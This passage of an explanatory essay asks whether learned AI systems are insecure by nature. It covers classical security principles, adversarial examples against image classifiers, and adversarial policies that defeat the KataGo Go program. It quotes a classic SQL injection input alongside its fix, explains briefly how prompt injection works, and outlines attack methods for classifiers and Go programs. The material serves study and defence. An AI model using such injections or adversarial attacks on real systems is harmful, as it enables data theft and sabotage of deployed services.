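# Whether AI systems are insecure by nature, and how such weakness differs from a planted backdoor

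## What computer security assumes, and how it classifies flaws

Computer security is the branch of engineering that tries to keep a computer system within the limits its owner has set, even when someone is working to push it past them. The field took shape around 1970, when organisations such as airlines and the US Air Force began letting many people share one machine. Its methods suit programs that people write as explicit rules.

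A growing share of software consists of *learned systems*, programs whose behaviour is set by numbers fitted to data, called weights, rather than by rules a person wrote. Image classifiers, modern Go-playing programs and the language models behind AI assistants are all learned systems, and attackers have found ways to make each of them fail. The cause may be an *inherent weakness*, which arises from how the system learns or is designed and which nobody intended as a way in. It may also be a *planted backdoor*, a hidden behaviour that someone deliberately added to trigger later. The two can look alike from outside, but they call for different defences. Researchers disagree about how much inherent weakness anyone can remove.

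### One program and its guard

*The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, a 1975 tutorial by Saltzer and Schroeder, uses an airline's seat reservation program as an example. A reservation agent can make bookings, and can cancel them for passengers the agent can name. A boarding agent can also print the full passenger list for the flights they handle. The airline may want to keep that list from reservation agents, so that a police request for it reaches the right level of management. The program therefore serves people with different authority, and the system has to enforce that difference.

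A *trust boundary* is the line in a system where data or requests pass between parts trusted to different degrees. At the airline, it runs between the agents' terminals and the central computer that holds the bookings. Removing the "print list" button from a reservation agent's screen adds little security, because an agent with some technical skill can send the request without the button. The central computer has to check the request itself. Saltzer and Schroeder picture a wall around each thing worth protecting, with a door in it and a guard who compares something the guard knows with something the visitor holds.

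This guard, which security engineers call a *reference monitor*, checks every request against the security policy before allowing it. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), a report for the US Air Force, set three conditions for it. It must be impossible to tamper with, the system must invoke it every time, and it must be small enough to analyse and test completely. The policy can be as simple as a table, with users and programs down the side, files and devices along the top, and the permitted actions in each cell. The cell for a reservation agent and a flight's passenger list would be empty, because the agent isn't permitted to do anything with that list.

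*Complete mediation* is the rule that no request may skip the check. Saltzer and Schroeder extend it to start-up, recovery and maintenance, and they distrust any shortcut in which the system remembers an earlier answer. If the airline moves a boarding agent to another job at noon, an approval that the program stored at nine is wrong by the afternoon. *Least privilege* means giving each user and each program only the permissions that its job requires, which limits the damage when something fails. The part of the program that prints boarding passes does not need permission to change fares, and if the airline withholds it, an attacker who takes over that part still cannot change them.

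The parts that must work correctly for a system's security to hold make up its *trusted computing base*. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper from researchers at Google, Nvidia, three US universities and two other groups, includes among these parts the operating system, the mechanisms that isolate programs from one another, the policy and the reference monitor. "Trusted" means that everyone depends on these parts, whether or not they deserve it. The software that draws the seat map on an agent's screen can stay outside the trusted computing base because a fault there may annoy passengers but does not give anyone a list they should not have.

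Anderson's third condition, that the monitor be small enough to analyse completely, was the hardest for the systems of the day to meet. On one Honeywell computer, a hardware register confined each user's program to its own area of memory, but most of the operating system ran with that check suspended, so the monitor was not always at work. Treating the whole operating system as the monitor would not have solved the problem, because it and its supporting software ran to between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many for anyone to analyse completely. Testing could not make up for this. The Air Force already knew of "tiger teams", specialists who try to break into a system to expose its flaws. No known team had yet failed, but Anderson pointed out that if one did, the owner would learn only that the system's security was unknown. Saltzer and Schroeder attribute the difficulty to security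 being a negative requirement. A system must prevent all unauthorised use, so a proof of its security has to cover every possible threat.

The classical approach was to make a system's security depend on a small component and reason about that component exhaustively. This works only if people can tell from the component's code what it will do with inputs nobody has tried, and if there is a clear line between what is trusted and what is not.

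### Instructions and data

Databases show how much such a line can achieve. Many programs fetch records by sending a database a command, or query, in a language called SQL. A careless developer builds the query by pasting whatever the customer typed into the middle of it. In an example adapted from OWASP's *SQL Injection Prevention Cheat Sheet*, a guide from a non-profit organisation for web security, a customer who types `tom` produces a harmless query:

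```
SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = 'tom'
```

An attacker types `tom' or '1'='1` instead, and the same pasting gives:

```
SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = 'tom' or '1'='1'
```

The attacker's quotation mark closes the name early, so the database reads the rest as part of the command. Since 1 always equals 1, the condition holds for every row, and the database returns everyone's balance. The database is working correctly, but the program has joined a developer's instructions and a stranger's data into one string, so the database cannot distinguish them. Security engineers call this attack SQL injection.

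The repair is a *parameterised query*, also called a prepared statement:

```
SELECT account_balance FROM user_data WHERE user_name = ?
```

The developer first defines the whole command, with a placeholder for the name, and then passes the name in as a value. Given the same attack, the database looks for a customer whose name is exactly `tom' or '1'='1` and finds none. According to OWASP, the database will always distinguish code from data, whatever the user supplies. Processors enforce the same separation in hardware, where a no-execute bit marks a region of memory as data and the processor will not run anything stored there.

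This repair doesn't require a list of known attacks or a guess about whether an input looks suspicious. Some developers try to clean the input instead. *Malicious Cyber Actors Use SQL Injection Vulnerabilities to Compromise Systems* (2024), an alert to software manufacturers from the US agencies CISA and the FBI, calls that approach brittle, hard to enforce at scale and often possible to bypass.

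A parameterised query protects only the programs that use one. MySQL, a widely used database, has offered prepared statements since 2004. Twenty years later, the agencies issued their alert because attackers had used SQL injection in a single file-transfer product to harm thousands of organisations. SQL injection ranks second in MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025), an annual ranking from a US non-profit, up from third the year before. The attack is still common because developers often fail to apply a well-known fix, which is a different problem from having no fix.

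### Where a learned system's behaviour comes from

Suppose engineers want a program that labels photographs. They write a formula that turns a picture's brightness values into a score for each possible label. The formula contains a great many adjustable numbers, called weights, which start out random, so the first scores are worthless. To train the program, a computer runs the formula on a photograph whose correct label is known and measures the error, *L*. For each weight *w*, it calculates whether a slightly higher or lower value would have reduced the error, then moves the weight a small step in that direction by replacing *w* with *w* − *η* · ∂*L*/∂*w*, where *η* sets the size of the step. It repeats this over thousands or millions of photographs until the error is low. Language models acquire most of their abilities in the same way, except that the "label" is the next fragment of a text.

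Reviewers can read the formula and the training procedure line by line, since both are ordinary code, but neither contains a rule about cats. If the finished system mistakes a certain cat for a dog, engineers can't fix the error by correcting a line, because it results from a vast number of weights acting together, most of which also contribute to right answers. They can train the system further on more pictures of cats, but this changes the weights that all the other labels depend on, and they discover the side effects by testing.

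With its settings fixed, a learned system can give the same output for the same input every time, but there is no short text from which a person could work out its output for an input that nobody has tried. Anderson's demand for complete analysis presupposes such a text. Researchers can trace some behaviour to particular groups of weights, but they have no complete account of this kind for a large model.

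### Sorting flaws by origin

*A Taxonomy of Computer Program Security Flaws, with Examples* (Landwehr, Bull and colleagues, 1994) classifies 50 documented flaws by how they entered the system, when they entered and where they were located. It defines a flaw broadly, as any part of a program that can cause the system to break its security rules. The classification by how flaws entered first separates *inadvertent* flaws from *intentional* ones, then divides the intentional flaws into *malicious* and *non-malicious*.

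Inadvertent flaws are bugs, such as a program failing to check its input or leaving one user's deleted data where another can read it. Landwehr and colleagues put 32 of the 50 cases in this category. Ten are malicious, among them viruses and other Trojan horses (programs that pose as something useful while exploiting the rights of whoever runs them). The remaining eight are intentional but non-malicious, meaning that someone deliberately added a feature that also created a security hole. For instance, a facility for debugging a system remotely may also let an intruder in. Landwehr and colleagues caution that the sample is not representative, so the proportions are weak evidence about software at large.

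The malicious flaw closest to a planted backdoor is the *trapdoor*, hidden code that lets anyone who enters a special input bypass the normal checks. Landwehr and colleagues illustrate it with a cash machine. Normally, the program allows a withdrawal if the number typed matches the number on the card. A dishonest programmer adds "or if the number typed is 9999", so that 9999 works with every card. In machine learning, an input pattern that activates a backdoor, as 9999 does here, is called a *trigger*.

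Sorting flaws by origin is useful because the defences differ. If most flaws are accidents, more code review and testing should reduce them. If the serious ones are deliberate, Landwehr and colleagues expect those measures to help much less, and suggest spending on more trustworthy programmers and on attempts to break in. A reviewer would spot the 9999 at once, so a competent saboteur would hide the flaw better, for example in the machine-readable form of a program, which is hard for people to understand. Landwehr and colleagues cite Thompson's 1984 design for a compiler, the tool that translates source code into that form. When it translates the password check of the Unix operating system, this compiler inserts a trapdoor. Someone who reads the source code of the password check finds nothing wrong, and a file of weights gives a reader even less information.

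Landwehr and colleagues concede that intention is hard to characterise, but they think the line between malicious and accidental flaws should hold in practice because nobody is likely to create a Trojan horse by mistake. This is a good argument for hand-written code, since no programmer types "or 9999" by accident. It is weaker for learned systems, because training can produce a response to some odd pattern that no person chose. Finding such a response therefore does not show that someone planted it.

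Weber, Karger and Paradkar, in *A Software Flaw Taxonomy*, accept another objection, which they credit to Howard, who wrote an earlier classification. They argue that the flaw is the defect that let a virus or Trojan horse in, not the virus or Trojan horse itself. Their own scheme drops Trojan horses but keeps trapdoors and logic bombs (code that does its damage when certain conditions arise). If someone plants a backdoor in a model by corrupting its training data, the defect on this view lies in how the developer collected the data. Fixing that protects the next model, but the model already trained still contains the backdoor. A customer who receives only the finished weights cannot repair the supplier's data collection, so the broader usage of Landwehr and colleagues is more helpful to that customer.

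Aslam, another critic, wanted to leave motive out of the classification because it is hard to establish. Weber and colleagues disagree, citing an automatic tool that found many real flaws by checking whether programs compare user-supplied numbers against any limit, though not whether the limit is right. The tool works well when programmers forget the comparison, but a saboteur can defeat it by adding a meaningless one. Intent therefore determines which detection methods will work, even when nobody can establish it afterward, which matters to anyone inspecting a model.

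In these terms, inherent weakness includes both the inadvertent and the non-malicious classes. Flaws in the non-malicious class are harder to repair because they come with something the designers wanted. Landwehr and colleagues mention an early operating system that ran code from users' own memory with full system privileges. By the time people recognised the danger, other software depended on this behaviour, so the flaw stayed.

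### Three readings of "insecure by nature"

Saltzer and Schroeder wrote in 1975 that no one knew how to build a system without flaws, so "insecure by nature" has to mean more than "has flaws". Applied to learned systems, the phrase could refer to any of three claims, and evidence for one may be irrelevant to the others.

The boldest claim is that any system that learns from examples is insecure by nature. A finite set of examples leaves open what the system will do with every other input, and the attacker chooses the input. Establishing this claim would require a proof, or failures that recur across unrelated designs and survive every attempted repair under an *adaptive attacker*, who knows the defence and designs the attack against it. One learned system that withstood such attacks on a hard task would refute it. Some weaknesses in classical computer security are nearly as fundamental. A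 *covert channel* is a path for information that the designers never intended. For example, a program with access to secrets can make a shared machine run slower or faster in a pattern that another program reads as a code. Landwehr and colleagues observe that the channels that are hardest to remove arise from essential requirements of the system. To remove them completely, a designer would have to give up some of the sharing that the machine exists to provide.

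A more modest claim is that language models are insecure as currently designed. Database queries built by pasting in untrusted input were insecure, but databases didn't require pasting, and the fix left them as useful as before. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes a similar flaw in language models. The developer's instructions, the user's request and any document the model reads all arrive as a single stream of text fragments, so a sentence in a document can act as a command (an attack known as prompt injection). Someone may devise a model with a true equivalent of the placeholder. The paper doubts this, and conjectures that persistent attackers will always get around a separation that depends on the model, because attackers have broken earlier defences. That record is serious evidence for the conjecture but doesn't prove it.

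The last claim is about deployment, meaning what people connect the system to and how much authority they give it. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* puts the model outside the trusted computing base and leaves enforcement to a reference monitor. A forbidden action that the monitor blocks in time does not count as a security violation, whatever led the model to propose it. Anderson took a similar view of the computers of 1972. Nobody could certify the Honeywell machines for users who wrote their own programs, but a secure query service on the same family of machines was feasible if its users could only submit queries and its builders were reliable.

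Restricting what a system may do only helps when the harm is an action that a policy can describe, such as sending a file to a stranger. If the system's only job is to identify what a photograph shows, the harm is a wrong answer, and a monitor that could recognise wrong answers would have to be a better classifier than the system itself.

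## Image classifiers fooled by changes too small to see

Attackers can produce such wrong answers almost at will. In *Intriguing properties of neural networks*, Szegedy, Zaremba and colleagues (2013) slightly altered photographs that AlexNet, a well-known image classifier, had labelled correctly. The two versions of each picture looked alike, but AlexNet labelled the altered ones "ostrich", whatever they showed. The typical alteration changed a pixel's brightness by about 0.65% of the full range, less than two of the 255 steps in an ordinary digital image. They named these inputs *adversarial examples*. The term now covers any input that someone has altered, usually slightly, to make a learned system get it wrong.

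### Making one

AlexNet is a neural network, a learned system that passes its input through layers of simple arithmetic. Training adjusts the network's weights to reduce its error on a fixed set of pictures, whereas the attack keeps the weights fixed and adjusts the pixels. Given a picture *x* and a false label *l*, the attacker looks for the smallest change *r* that makes the network label *x* + *r* as *l*. Finding the exact minimum is hard, so Szegedy and colleagues minimised *c*·|*r*| + *L*(*x* + *r*, *l*) instead, where *L* is the network's error measured against the false label and *c* sets how much the size of the change counts. They found an adversarial example for every picture they tried, on every network they studied.

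A year later, *Explaining and Harnessing Adversarial Examples* (Goodfellow, Shlens and Szegedy, 2014) introduced a method that needs less computation. It finds in a single calculation whether brightening or darkening each pixel would raise the classifier's error, then shifts every pixel by the same small amount in the direction that raises it.

Both methods need the weights, which an attacker may not have, but adversarial examples often transfer from one network to another. Szegedy and colleagues altered images of handwritten digits to fool a simple linear classifier, then tested them on a separate network with two hidden layers. That network got 48.1% of them wrong, while random noise about twice as strong caused only 5% errors. Transfer is unreliable, since the rate was as low as 2% for other pairs of models, but it worked even between networks trained on separate halves of the data. An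 attacker without the weights can therefore train a substitute on similar data, attack that, and try the results on the real target. The attacker doesn't need to know a secret code, like the 9999 that the cash machine accepts.

Ordinary testing does not reveal the problem. Szegedy and colleagues also added random noise so heavy that people could hardly read the digits, and a network still classified 51% of them correctly. The adversarial versions had far smaller changes, but the same network classified none of them correctly.

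### Why a boundary might always be close

Many image classifiers accept pictures of 224 by 224 pixels, with three colour values per pixel, or 150,528 numbers in total. Each picture is a point in a space with one dimension per number, and the classifier divides that space into regions, one per label. A picture has an adversarial example if a boundary between regions runs close to it.

A simple case shows why a very small change can be enough to fool a classifier. Suppose each of the *d* numbers in an input *x* is drawn independently from a Gaussian with mean 0 and variance 1. A linear classifier multiplies each number by a weight, adds the results, and outputs "cat" if the total *w*·*x* is positive and "dog" if it is negative. The distance from *x* to the boundary between the two labels is |*w*·*x*| / ‖*w*‖, where ‖*w*‖ is the length of the weight vector. This distance is the size of *x*'s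 component along one direction. That component follows the same Gaussian however large *d* is, so the average distance is always √(2/π), or about 0.8. The length of *x*, however, grows as about √*d*, because each extra number adds about 1 to the squared length. On average, an attacker must therefore change the input by about 8% of its length when *d* = 100, but by only about 0.2% when *d* = 150,528, where the length is about 388.

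The change has to point towards the classifier's decision boundary. A random change of the same length moves the image towards or away from the boundary by only about 1/388 of that length, which fits the finding that networks tolerate random noise but fail when someone searches for a change that fools them.

Real classifiers have curved boundaries, but Shafahi, Huang and colleagues (2018), in *Are adversarial examples inevitable?*, proved a similar result for boundaries of any shape. In their simplest case the inputs lie on the surface of a sphere of radius 1 in *n* dimensions. Take a class whose region covers at most half of the sphere. Everything outside the region then covers at least half. Now expand that outside part by a distance *ε* in every direction. A classical theorem of geometry, the isoperimetric inequality, implies that the expansion covers at least as much as it would if the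 outside part were a perfect hemisphere, and in high dimensions even a hemisphere swallows nearly the whole sphere after a small expansion. The only safe inputs are those the expansion misses. A random member of the class is therefore either already misclassified or within *ε* of a different label with probability at least

1 − *V* · √(π/8) · exp(−(*n* − 1)*ε*²/2)

where *V* is the density of the class at its densest point, compared with an even spread over the sphere. If a class spreads evenly over half the sphere, *V* is 2. With *n* = 150,528 and *ε* = 0.01, the formula puts more than 99.9% of its members within reach of the attacker.

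*The Curse of Concentration in Robust Learning* (Mahloujifar, Diochnos and Mahmoody, 2018) starts from the mistakes a classifier already makes. Suppose it gets 1% of inputs wrong. In many high-dimensional spaces, at least half of all inputs lie within a short distance of any set that holds 1% of them, and nearly all lie within another short distance. This property is called *concentration of measure*. Where it holds, for any classifier with a small constant error rate, almost every input can be changed slightly so that the classifier gets it wrong. The result shows that these changes exist, but an attacker still has to find them. *Computational Concentration of Measure* (2019) proves that an efficient search will succeed for certain input distributions.

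### Whether photographs fit the theorem

If these proofs applied to photographs, image classification would be insecure by nature in the strongest sense, and no training method could help. But the proofs depend on assumptions about how images are distributed. In the sphere example, the guarantee disappears once the densest part of a class is about 3,000 times denser than an even spread. Photographs probably exceed that by an enormous factor, since neighbouring pixels tend to match and almost every random arrangement of pixels looks like static. *A Simple Explanation for the Existence of Adversarial Examples* (2019) also argues that if natural pictures sit far from any boundary between classes, a theorem about typical points of the space does not explain why attackers can alter them to fool a classifier.

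Shafahi and colleagues' theorem assumes nothing about how the classifier works, so it covers a person sorting pictures as well as a network. But as Salvatore, Fort and Ganguli (2026) point out in *Solving adversarial examples requires solving exponential misalignment*, the changes that fool networks do not fool people. Photographs must therefore violate the theorem's assumptions, at least for changes this small. This objection does not affect the version that starts from mistakes, because people's labels define what counts as a mistake, though only measurement can settle whether that version applies.

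Shafahi and colleagues doubted that the number of dimensions makes classifiers easy to fool. They enlarged the handwritten digits of MNIST, a standard test set, by replacing each pixel with a block of identical pixels. This multiplies the dimensions, but they proved that the best possible resistance to attack, relative to the size of the image, stays the same. They also compared enlarged digits with CIFAR-10, a set of tiny colour photographs in ten classes. The CIFAR-10 classifiers were far easier to fool, although both sets of images have about 3,100 dimensions. They attribute the difference to the greater variety of the photographs, and conclude that the question of whether adversarial examples are inevitable is ill-posed unless the data, the attacker and the measure of distance are specified.

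Mahloujifar, Zhang and colleagues (2019) made this measurement in *Empirically Measuring Concentration*. For a given number of mistakes, they looked for the set that put the fewest other pictures within the attacker's reach. Their method draws boxes around dense clusters of similar pictures and places the mistakes outside all the boxes. For CIFAR-10, the attacker could change each colour value by up to 8 of the 255 steps. With an ordinary error rate close to that of a leading robust classifier of the time, they found a set that left 29.21% of pictures exposed, while the actual classifier failed on 52.96% under attack. For the digits, the two figures were close, at 8.28% and 10.70%.

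Concentration could thus explain most of the failures on digits, but not on photographs. Even 29.21% may overstate the failures that the geometry makes unavoidable, since a better search could find a less harmful set of mistakes. *It Is All About Data* (2023), a survey, describes later estimates of achievable robustness that are higher. However, nobody has shown that training can produce a classifier whose only mistakes are in such a set.

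Salvatore and colleagues also give a geometric explanation, but theirs concerns what the network has learned. They estimate that the photographs in a typical class vary along only about 20 independent directions. The images that a standard network assigns to a class with high confidence vary along more than 130,000 of the 150,528 possible directions, and most of them look like noise to a person. A region that extends in nearly every direction passes close to any picture. Across 18 networks trained on CIFAR-10, those that resisted attack better had regions with fewer dimensions, but even the best had about 250, compared with about 10 for the photographs. This is a correlation, and it does not explain why training produces such high-dimensional regions.

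### Real patterns that break easily

*Adversarial Examples Are Not Bugs, They Are Features* (Ilyas, Santurkar and colleagues, 2019) traces the problem to the data and the goal of training. Ordinary training rewards a classifier only for being right, so the classifier will use any pattern that helps. Ears and tails help identify a cat, but faint textures that people never notice may help too. Ilyas and colleagues call a pattern useful if it correlates with the correct label, and robust if it still does after an attacker has made the worst permitted change. A faint texture can be useful without being robust. If an attacker replaces the cat texture with a dog texture, a network that relies on such textures changes its answer.

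"Adversarial Examples Are Not Bugs, They Are Features" describes a test using a training set that looks completely mislabelled. Each CIFAR-10 picture was altered slightly until a standard network gave it a different label, and that false label was recorded as correct. In one version the false labels followed a fixed rule, so that every picture of one animal, for example, carried the name of a particular other class. A new network was trained on these pictures and tested on unaltered photographs with their true labels. If the alterations had been meaningless quirks of the first network, the visible content would have taught the new one to give wrong answers. Instead it labelled 43.7% of the photographs correctly, where guessing would give 10%, so the alterations must have carried real information about the classes. When the false labels were random, the figure was 63.3%, against 95.3% for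 a network trained on the original data.

This also explains why an attack made for one network can fool another, because networks that learn from similar data pick up similar faint patterns. Ilyas and colleagues trained five network designs on the mislabelled pictures, and transferred attacks most often fooled the designs that had learned most from those pictures.

This explanation is incomplete. Another researcher, Nakkiran, constructed adversarial examples that carry no such useful patterns, and Ilyas and colleagues accept that other causes may exist. In the version with random labels, a little of the accuracy may come from visible features that leaked through. This is less of a concern for the 43.7% result, because the visible features there pointed to the wrong answer. This explanation still has the most direct support of those here, because Ilyas and colleagues changed the supposed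 cause and observed the effect in real photographs.

On this view, networks are vulnerable because they are trained only for accuracy, on data that contains useful but fragile patterns, so adversarial examples are not evidence of sabotage. However, a saboteur can design a backdoor to mimic them.

### Training on the attacks

If ordinary training rewards fragile patterns, one remedy is to stop rewarding them. *Adversarial training* does this by attacking the network while it learns. The standard form comes from Madry, Makelov and colleagues (2017), in *Towards Deep Learning Models Resistant to Adversarial Attacks*. Ordinary training looks for weights *w* that make the average error on the training pictures small. Adversarial training looks for weights that make this quantity small instead:

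average over (*x*, *y*) of max over permitted *δ* of *L*(*w*, *x* + *δ*, *y*)

Here *y* is the correct label and *δ* is any change within a set limit, such as 8 levels per colour value. For each batch of pictures, the computer searches for the most damaging change by taking several small steps that raise the error, pulling the picture back whenever it leaves the permitted range. It then adjusts the weights so that the network labels the altered pictures correctly. A pattern that an attacker can reverse within the limit no longer lowers the error, so the network learns to rely on it less. Running this search for every batch makes training considerably slower.

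Many other defences looked effective until attackers adapted to them. According to *A Review of Adversarial Attack and Defense for Classification Methods* (2021), Athalye and colleagues broke a group of defences from a single 2018 conference, but Madry's method held up. The public leaderboard RobustBench runs a standard set of strong attacks on published models. It lists three defences from 2019 and 2020 with less than 1% accuracy under these attacks.

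Surviving attacks does not guarantee that a network is robust. *Certified Adversarial Robustness via Randomized Smoothing* (Cohen, Rosenfeld and Kolter, 2019) explains that a failed attack on an adversarially trained network shows only that this attack failed. A better one may succeed, and Anderson saw the same limit in tiger teams.

### Voting under noise

Cohen and colleagues offer a proof instead. *Randomised smoothing* takes an existing classifier and asks it to label many copies of the same picture, each with fresh random noise added. The answer is the label that wins the most votes. A small change to the picture barely shifts the cloud of noisy copies, so it cannot shift the vote much either. If the winning label gets a share *p*₁ of the votes and the runner-up gets *p*₂, no change shorter than

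*R* = (*σ*/2) · (Φ⁻¹(*p*₁) − Φ⁻¹(*p*₂))

can alter the answer. The number *σ* is the strength of the noise, and Φ⁻¹ converts a probability into the matching position on the bell curve. With *σ* = 0.5, a winner at 90% and a runner-up at 10%, *R* is about 0.64, on a scale where each colour value runs from 0 to 1. The proof assumes nothing about the underlying classifier, so it holds against attacks that nobody has invented yet. The one qualification is that the computer must estimate the vote shares from a finite sample. This leaves a chance of error, which the user can make as small as they like by sampling more.

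The guarantee covers only small distances. A change of length 1 could move a thousand pixels by 8 steps each, or a single pixel across its entire range. The guarantee doesn't cover rotating the picture or putting a sticker on the object. The method also lowers accuracy considerably, because the classifier has to recognise pictures through heavy noise. On ImageNet, a set of photographs in 1,000 classes, Cohen and colleagues certified correct answers for 49% of pictures against changes of length 0.5, with a classifier that was right on 67% of unaltered pictures. For changes of length 2, the certified share fell to 19% and ordinary accuracy to 57%. The usual ImageNet attack test, which lets every colour value move by 4 steps, allows changes of length 6.

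Proofs also exist for the larger changes used in attack tests, but with a greater loss of accuracy. A small CIFAR-10 network from 2020, listed on RobustBench, has a provable accuracy of 32.24% against changes of 8 steps per colour value but labels only 44.73% of unaltered pictures correctly.

### How robust the best models are

*Robust accuracy* is the share of pictures a model still labels correctly when an attacker may alter each one within the limit. It depends on the attacks tried, so a model's score can only fall as attacks improve. Two 2026 studies add figures for ImageNet. *VanillaBench* (Bunzel, 2026) compared 186 robust models from RobustBench with undefended ones. *Adversarial robustness does not entail human-aligned categorization* (2026) tested robust ImageNet models on a sample of 1,000 pictures.

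| Test set and limit per colour value | Model | Ordinary accuracy | Robust accuracy |
|---|---|---|---|
| CIFAR-10, 8 steps | Undefended network | 94.78% | 0% |
| CIFAR-10, 8 steps | Highest on RobustBench (2024) | 93.68% | 73.71% |
| CIFAR-100, 8 steps | Highest on RobustBench (2023) | 75.22% | 42.66% |
| ImageNet, 4 steps | Average of 30 robust models | 73.12% | 46.69% |
| ImageNet, 4 steps | A strong individual model (2024) | 79.1% | 53.1% |

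RobustBench results show that classifiers are harder to defend on CIFAR-100, which has 100 classes, than on CIFAR-10, which has ten. Defenses on CIFAR-10 have improved, but slowly. Madry's network scores 44.04% under the current attacks, 30 points below the leader, which needed 300 million synthetic training images in addition to the original 50,000. No CIFAR-10 entry is newer than 2024, though stronger unsubmitted models may exist. Bunzel gives 75.28% as the best CIFAR-10 score, but RobustBench has since lowered that model's score to 73.10% after a stronger attack.

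The table understates the loss of accuracy because its undefended CIFAR-10 network is old. The best undefended models reach 99.5% on CIFAR-10 and 91% on ImageNet. When Bunzel matched each robust model with an undefended one of the same or a similar design, the robust models were on average 7.6 percentage points less accurate on CIFAR-10 and 8.5 points less accurate on ImageNet. This fits the idea that robust models don't use some of the patterns that make undefended models more accurate. It does not prove that the loss is unavoidable. Ilyas and colleagues constructed a simple artificial task in which ordinary training produces a fragile classifier even though a perfectly accurate and perfectly robust one exists.

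The leading CIFAR-10 model misclassifies 6.3% of ordinary pictures and 26.3% of pictures that an attacker has altered in ways that would not fool a person. For a classifier with about the same ordinary error rate, Mahloujifar, Zhang and colleagues found a set of mistakes that would expose only 18.1% of pictures to such attacks. The known geometry of the data therefore leaves room for better models.

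## A superhuman Go program that loses to weak opponents

Image classifiers make mistakes even on ordinary pictures, so their failures under attack might only mean that they are not yet good enough. The board game Go allows a cleaner test, because the best programs play it far better than any person. Wang, Gleave and colleagues (*Adversarial Policies Beat Superhuman Go AIs*, 2022) attacked KataGo, then the strongest publicly available Go program. The program they trained beat KataGo in 97% of games at a superhuman setting, but lost to a novice.

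In Go, two players take turns placing black and white stones on a grid, usually 19 lines by 19. Stones of one colour that are next to each other along the lines form a group, and the empty points beside a group are its liberties. A player captures a group by filling its last liberty. Whoever controls more of the board at the end wins.

KataGo learned by playing tens of millions of games against itself. For any position, its neural network produces a probability for each next move and an estimate of the chance of winning. The program uses both to search through possible continuations before it moves. The more positions it examines per move, the better it plays. Wang and colleagues estimate that without search it plays as well as a weak professional, and that it surpasses every human player when it examines more than about 128 positions per move.

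### Training an opponent for one victim

Wang and colleagues trained an adversary network in games against a frozen copy of KataGo. The adversary learned only from its own moves, so it learned to beat KataGo rather than imitate it. It planned each move by querying KataGo's network for the likely reply. An attacker therefore has to be able to run KataGo but doesn't need access to its weights. Since an untrained network would lose every game to the full program, the adversary started against early, weak versions of KataGo and moved on to stronger ones as it began to win.

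The first adversary exploited the way games end. A game ends when both players pass, and under the computer rules KataGo used, an empty area counts for a player only if no enemy stones are left in it. The adversary left stones in KataGo's territory that a person would have considered lost. KataGo, playing without search, passed too early. The adversary then passed as well and won on points. It won 99.9% of games after training with 0.13% of the computing power used to train KataGo.

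Wang and colleagues then stopped KataGo from passing while the result was still open, and this adversary lost every game. But the patch created a new flaw, because passing is sometimes the right move. Another adversary learned to set up positions where the patched program had to throw away its own stones.

Repeating the training against the patched program produced the *cyclic adversary*, which also beats KataGo without the patch. It won all 1,000 games against KataGo without search, and 97.3% of 1,000 games when KataGo examined 4,096 positions per move. In 50 games at each of two higher settings, it won 82% at one million positions per move and 72% at ten million, which takes KataGo more than an hour per move on high-end consumer hardware. Training the adversary took at most 14% of the computing power used to train KataGo.

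The cyclic adversary is nevertheless a poor Go player. One of Wang's co-authors, a novice, beat it, and after more than 2,300 games on a public server it ranked at about novice level. As in rock-paper-scissors, the adversary beats KataGo, KataGo beats professionals, and amateurs beat the adversary. The adversary therefore wins by exploiting a particular flaw in KataGo.

### The ring

The adversary first places a small group of stones that looks doomed. KataGo surrounds it with stones that join into a closed ring. Over the next hundred or so moves, the adversary builds a wall around the ring. KataGo could still save the ring, for example by capturing the small group inside it. Instead it plays elsewhere and typically estimates its chance of winning at over 99%, often until one move before the adversary captures the whole ring. Losing so many stones decides the game. Wang and colleagues think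 even someone who had played for only a few months might find the saving move.

David Wu, KataGo's creator, suspects that the network miscounts liberties. Information spreads through the network from each point to its neighbours, and on a ring it comes back to where it started. If the network cannot detect that it has already counted a liberty, it will count the same one repeatedly and rate the ring as safe. In a comment on the online essay *There are (probably) no superhuman Go AIs*, Wu reports that the misjudgement often disappears when someone edits the position to break the ring but leaves the rest of the fight intact.

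Wang and colleagues compared the network's internal activity on pairs of positions like these. The clearest differences were in a few channels of the 26th layer, though the error may begin earlier. They could make this comparison because they already knew from the attack which positions to examine. KataGo had been public since 2019, and many enthusiasts and professionals had used it, but as far as Wang and colleagues know, nobody had exploited the weakness before.

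People can carry out the attack without a computer's help. Kellin Pelrine, a co-author and Go expert, studied the adversary's games and then won 14 out of 15 against a top-ranked KataGo bot on a public server. Pelrine won even after giving the bot nine extra stones at the start, an advantage that would let a human professional beat almost anyone. By comparison, Shin Jin-seo, the world's top-ranked player, beat KataGo two games to one in July 2026 (강, 2026, *'알파고 충격 10년' AI 넘어선 '신'의 한수…신진서, 카타고에 역전승*). Shin played carefully and conventionally, and needed a two-stone start. KataGo also had only 20 seconds per move, according to a report in the Chinese newspaper 羊城晚报 (2026, *韩国棋手申真谞九段，力克人工智能KataGo！*).

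Other Go programs have the same weakness. Without further training, the cyclic adversary won 6.1% of 132 games against Leela Zero and 3.5% of 142 games against ELF OpenGo. These rates are low, but the best human players almost never beat either program. People have since used the ring attack to beat both, as well as FineArt and Sai. The Chinese news report *围棋八冠王柯洁分享必赢AI方式* (凤凰网, August 2026) quoted the champion Ke Jie as saying that people can still beat the top programs by "playing dumb", even when the program starts with nine extra stones. His account is not a controlled test, but it matches what Pelrine did.

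### Three attempted repairs

In *Can Go AIs Be Adversarially Robust?* (2024), Tseng, McLean and colleagues tested three defences by training new adversaries against each. They wanted a program that makes no game-losing blunders an ordinary player would avoid, and that nobody can beat reliably using little computing power.

Wu had already begun the first defence, a form of adversarial training. From December 2022, some of KataGo's practice games started from hand-picked ring positions, at first 0.08% of them and later a few tenths of a percent. By May 2023 the original adversary could no longer beat KataGo when KataGo used search. Wang and colleagues then trained that adversary further, and it won 47% of games against KataGo searching 4,096 positions per move. Tseng and colleagues later beat two newer versions of KataGo with new ring attacks.

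An unrelated "gift" attack also beat one of these versions. KataGo lets the adversary capture two stones and would need to take one back, but the rules forbid the recapture because it would repeat an earlier board position. KataGo makes this mistake even though its network receives a list of the moves this rule forbids.

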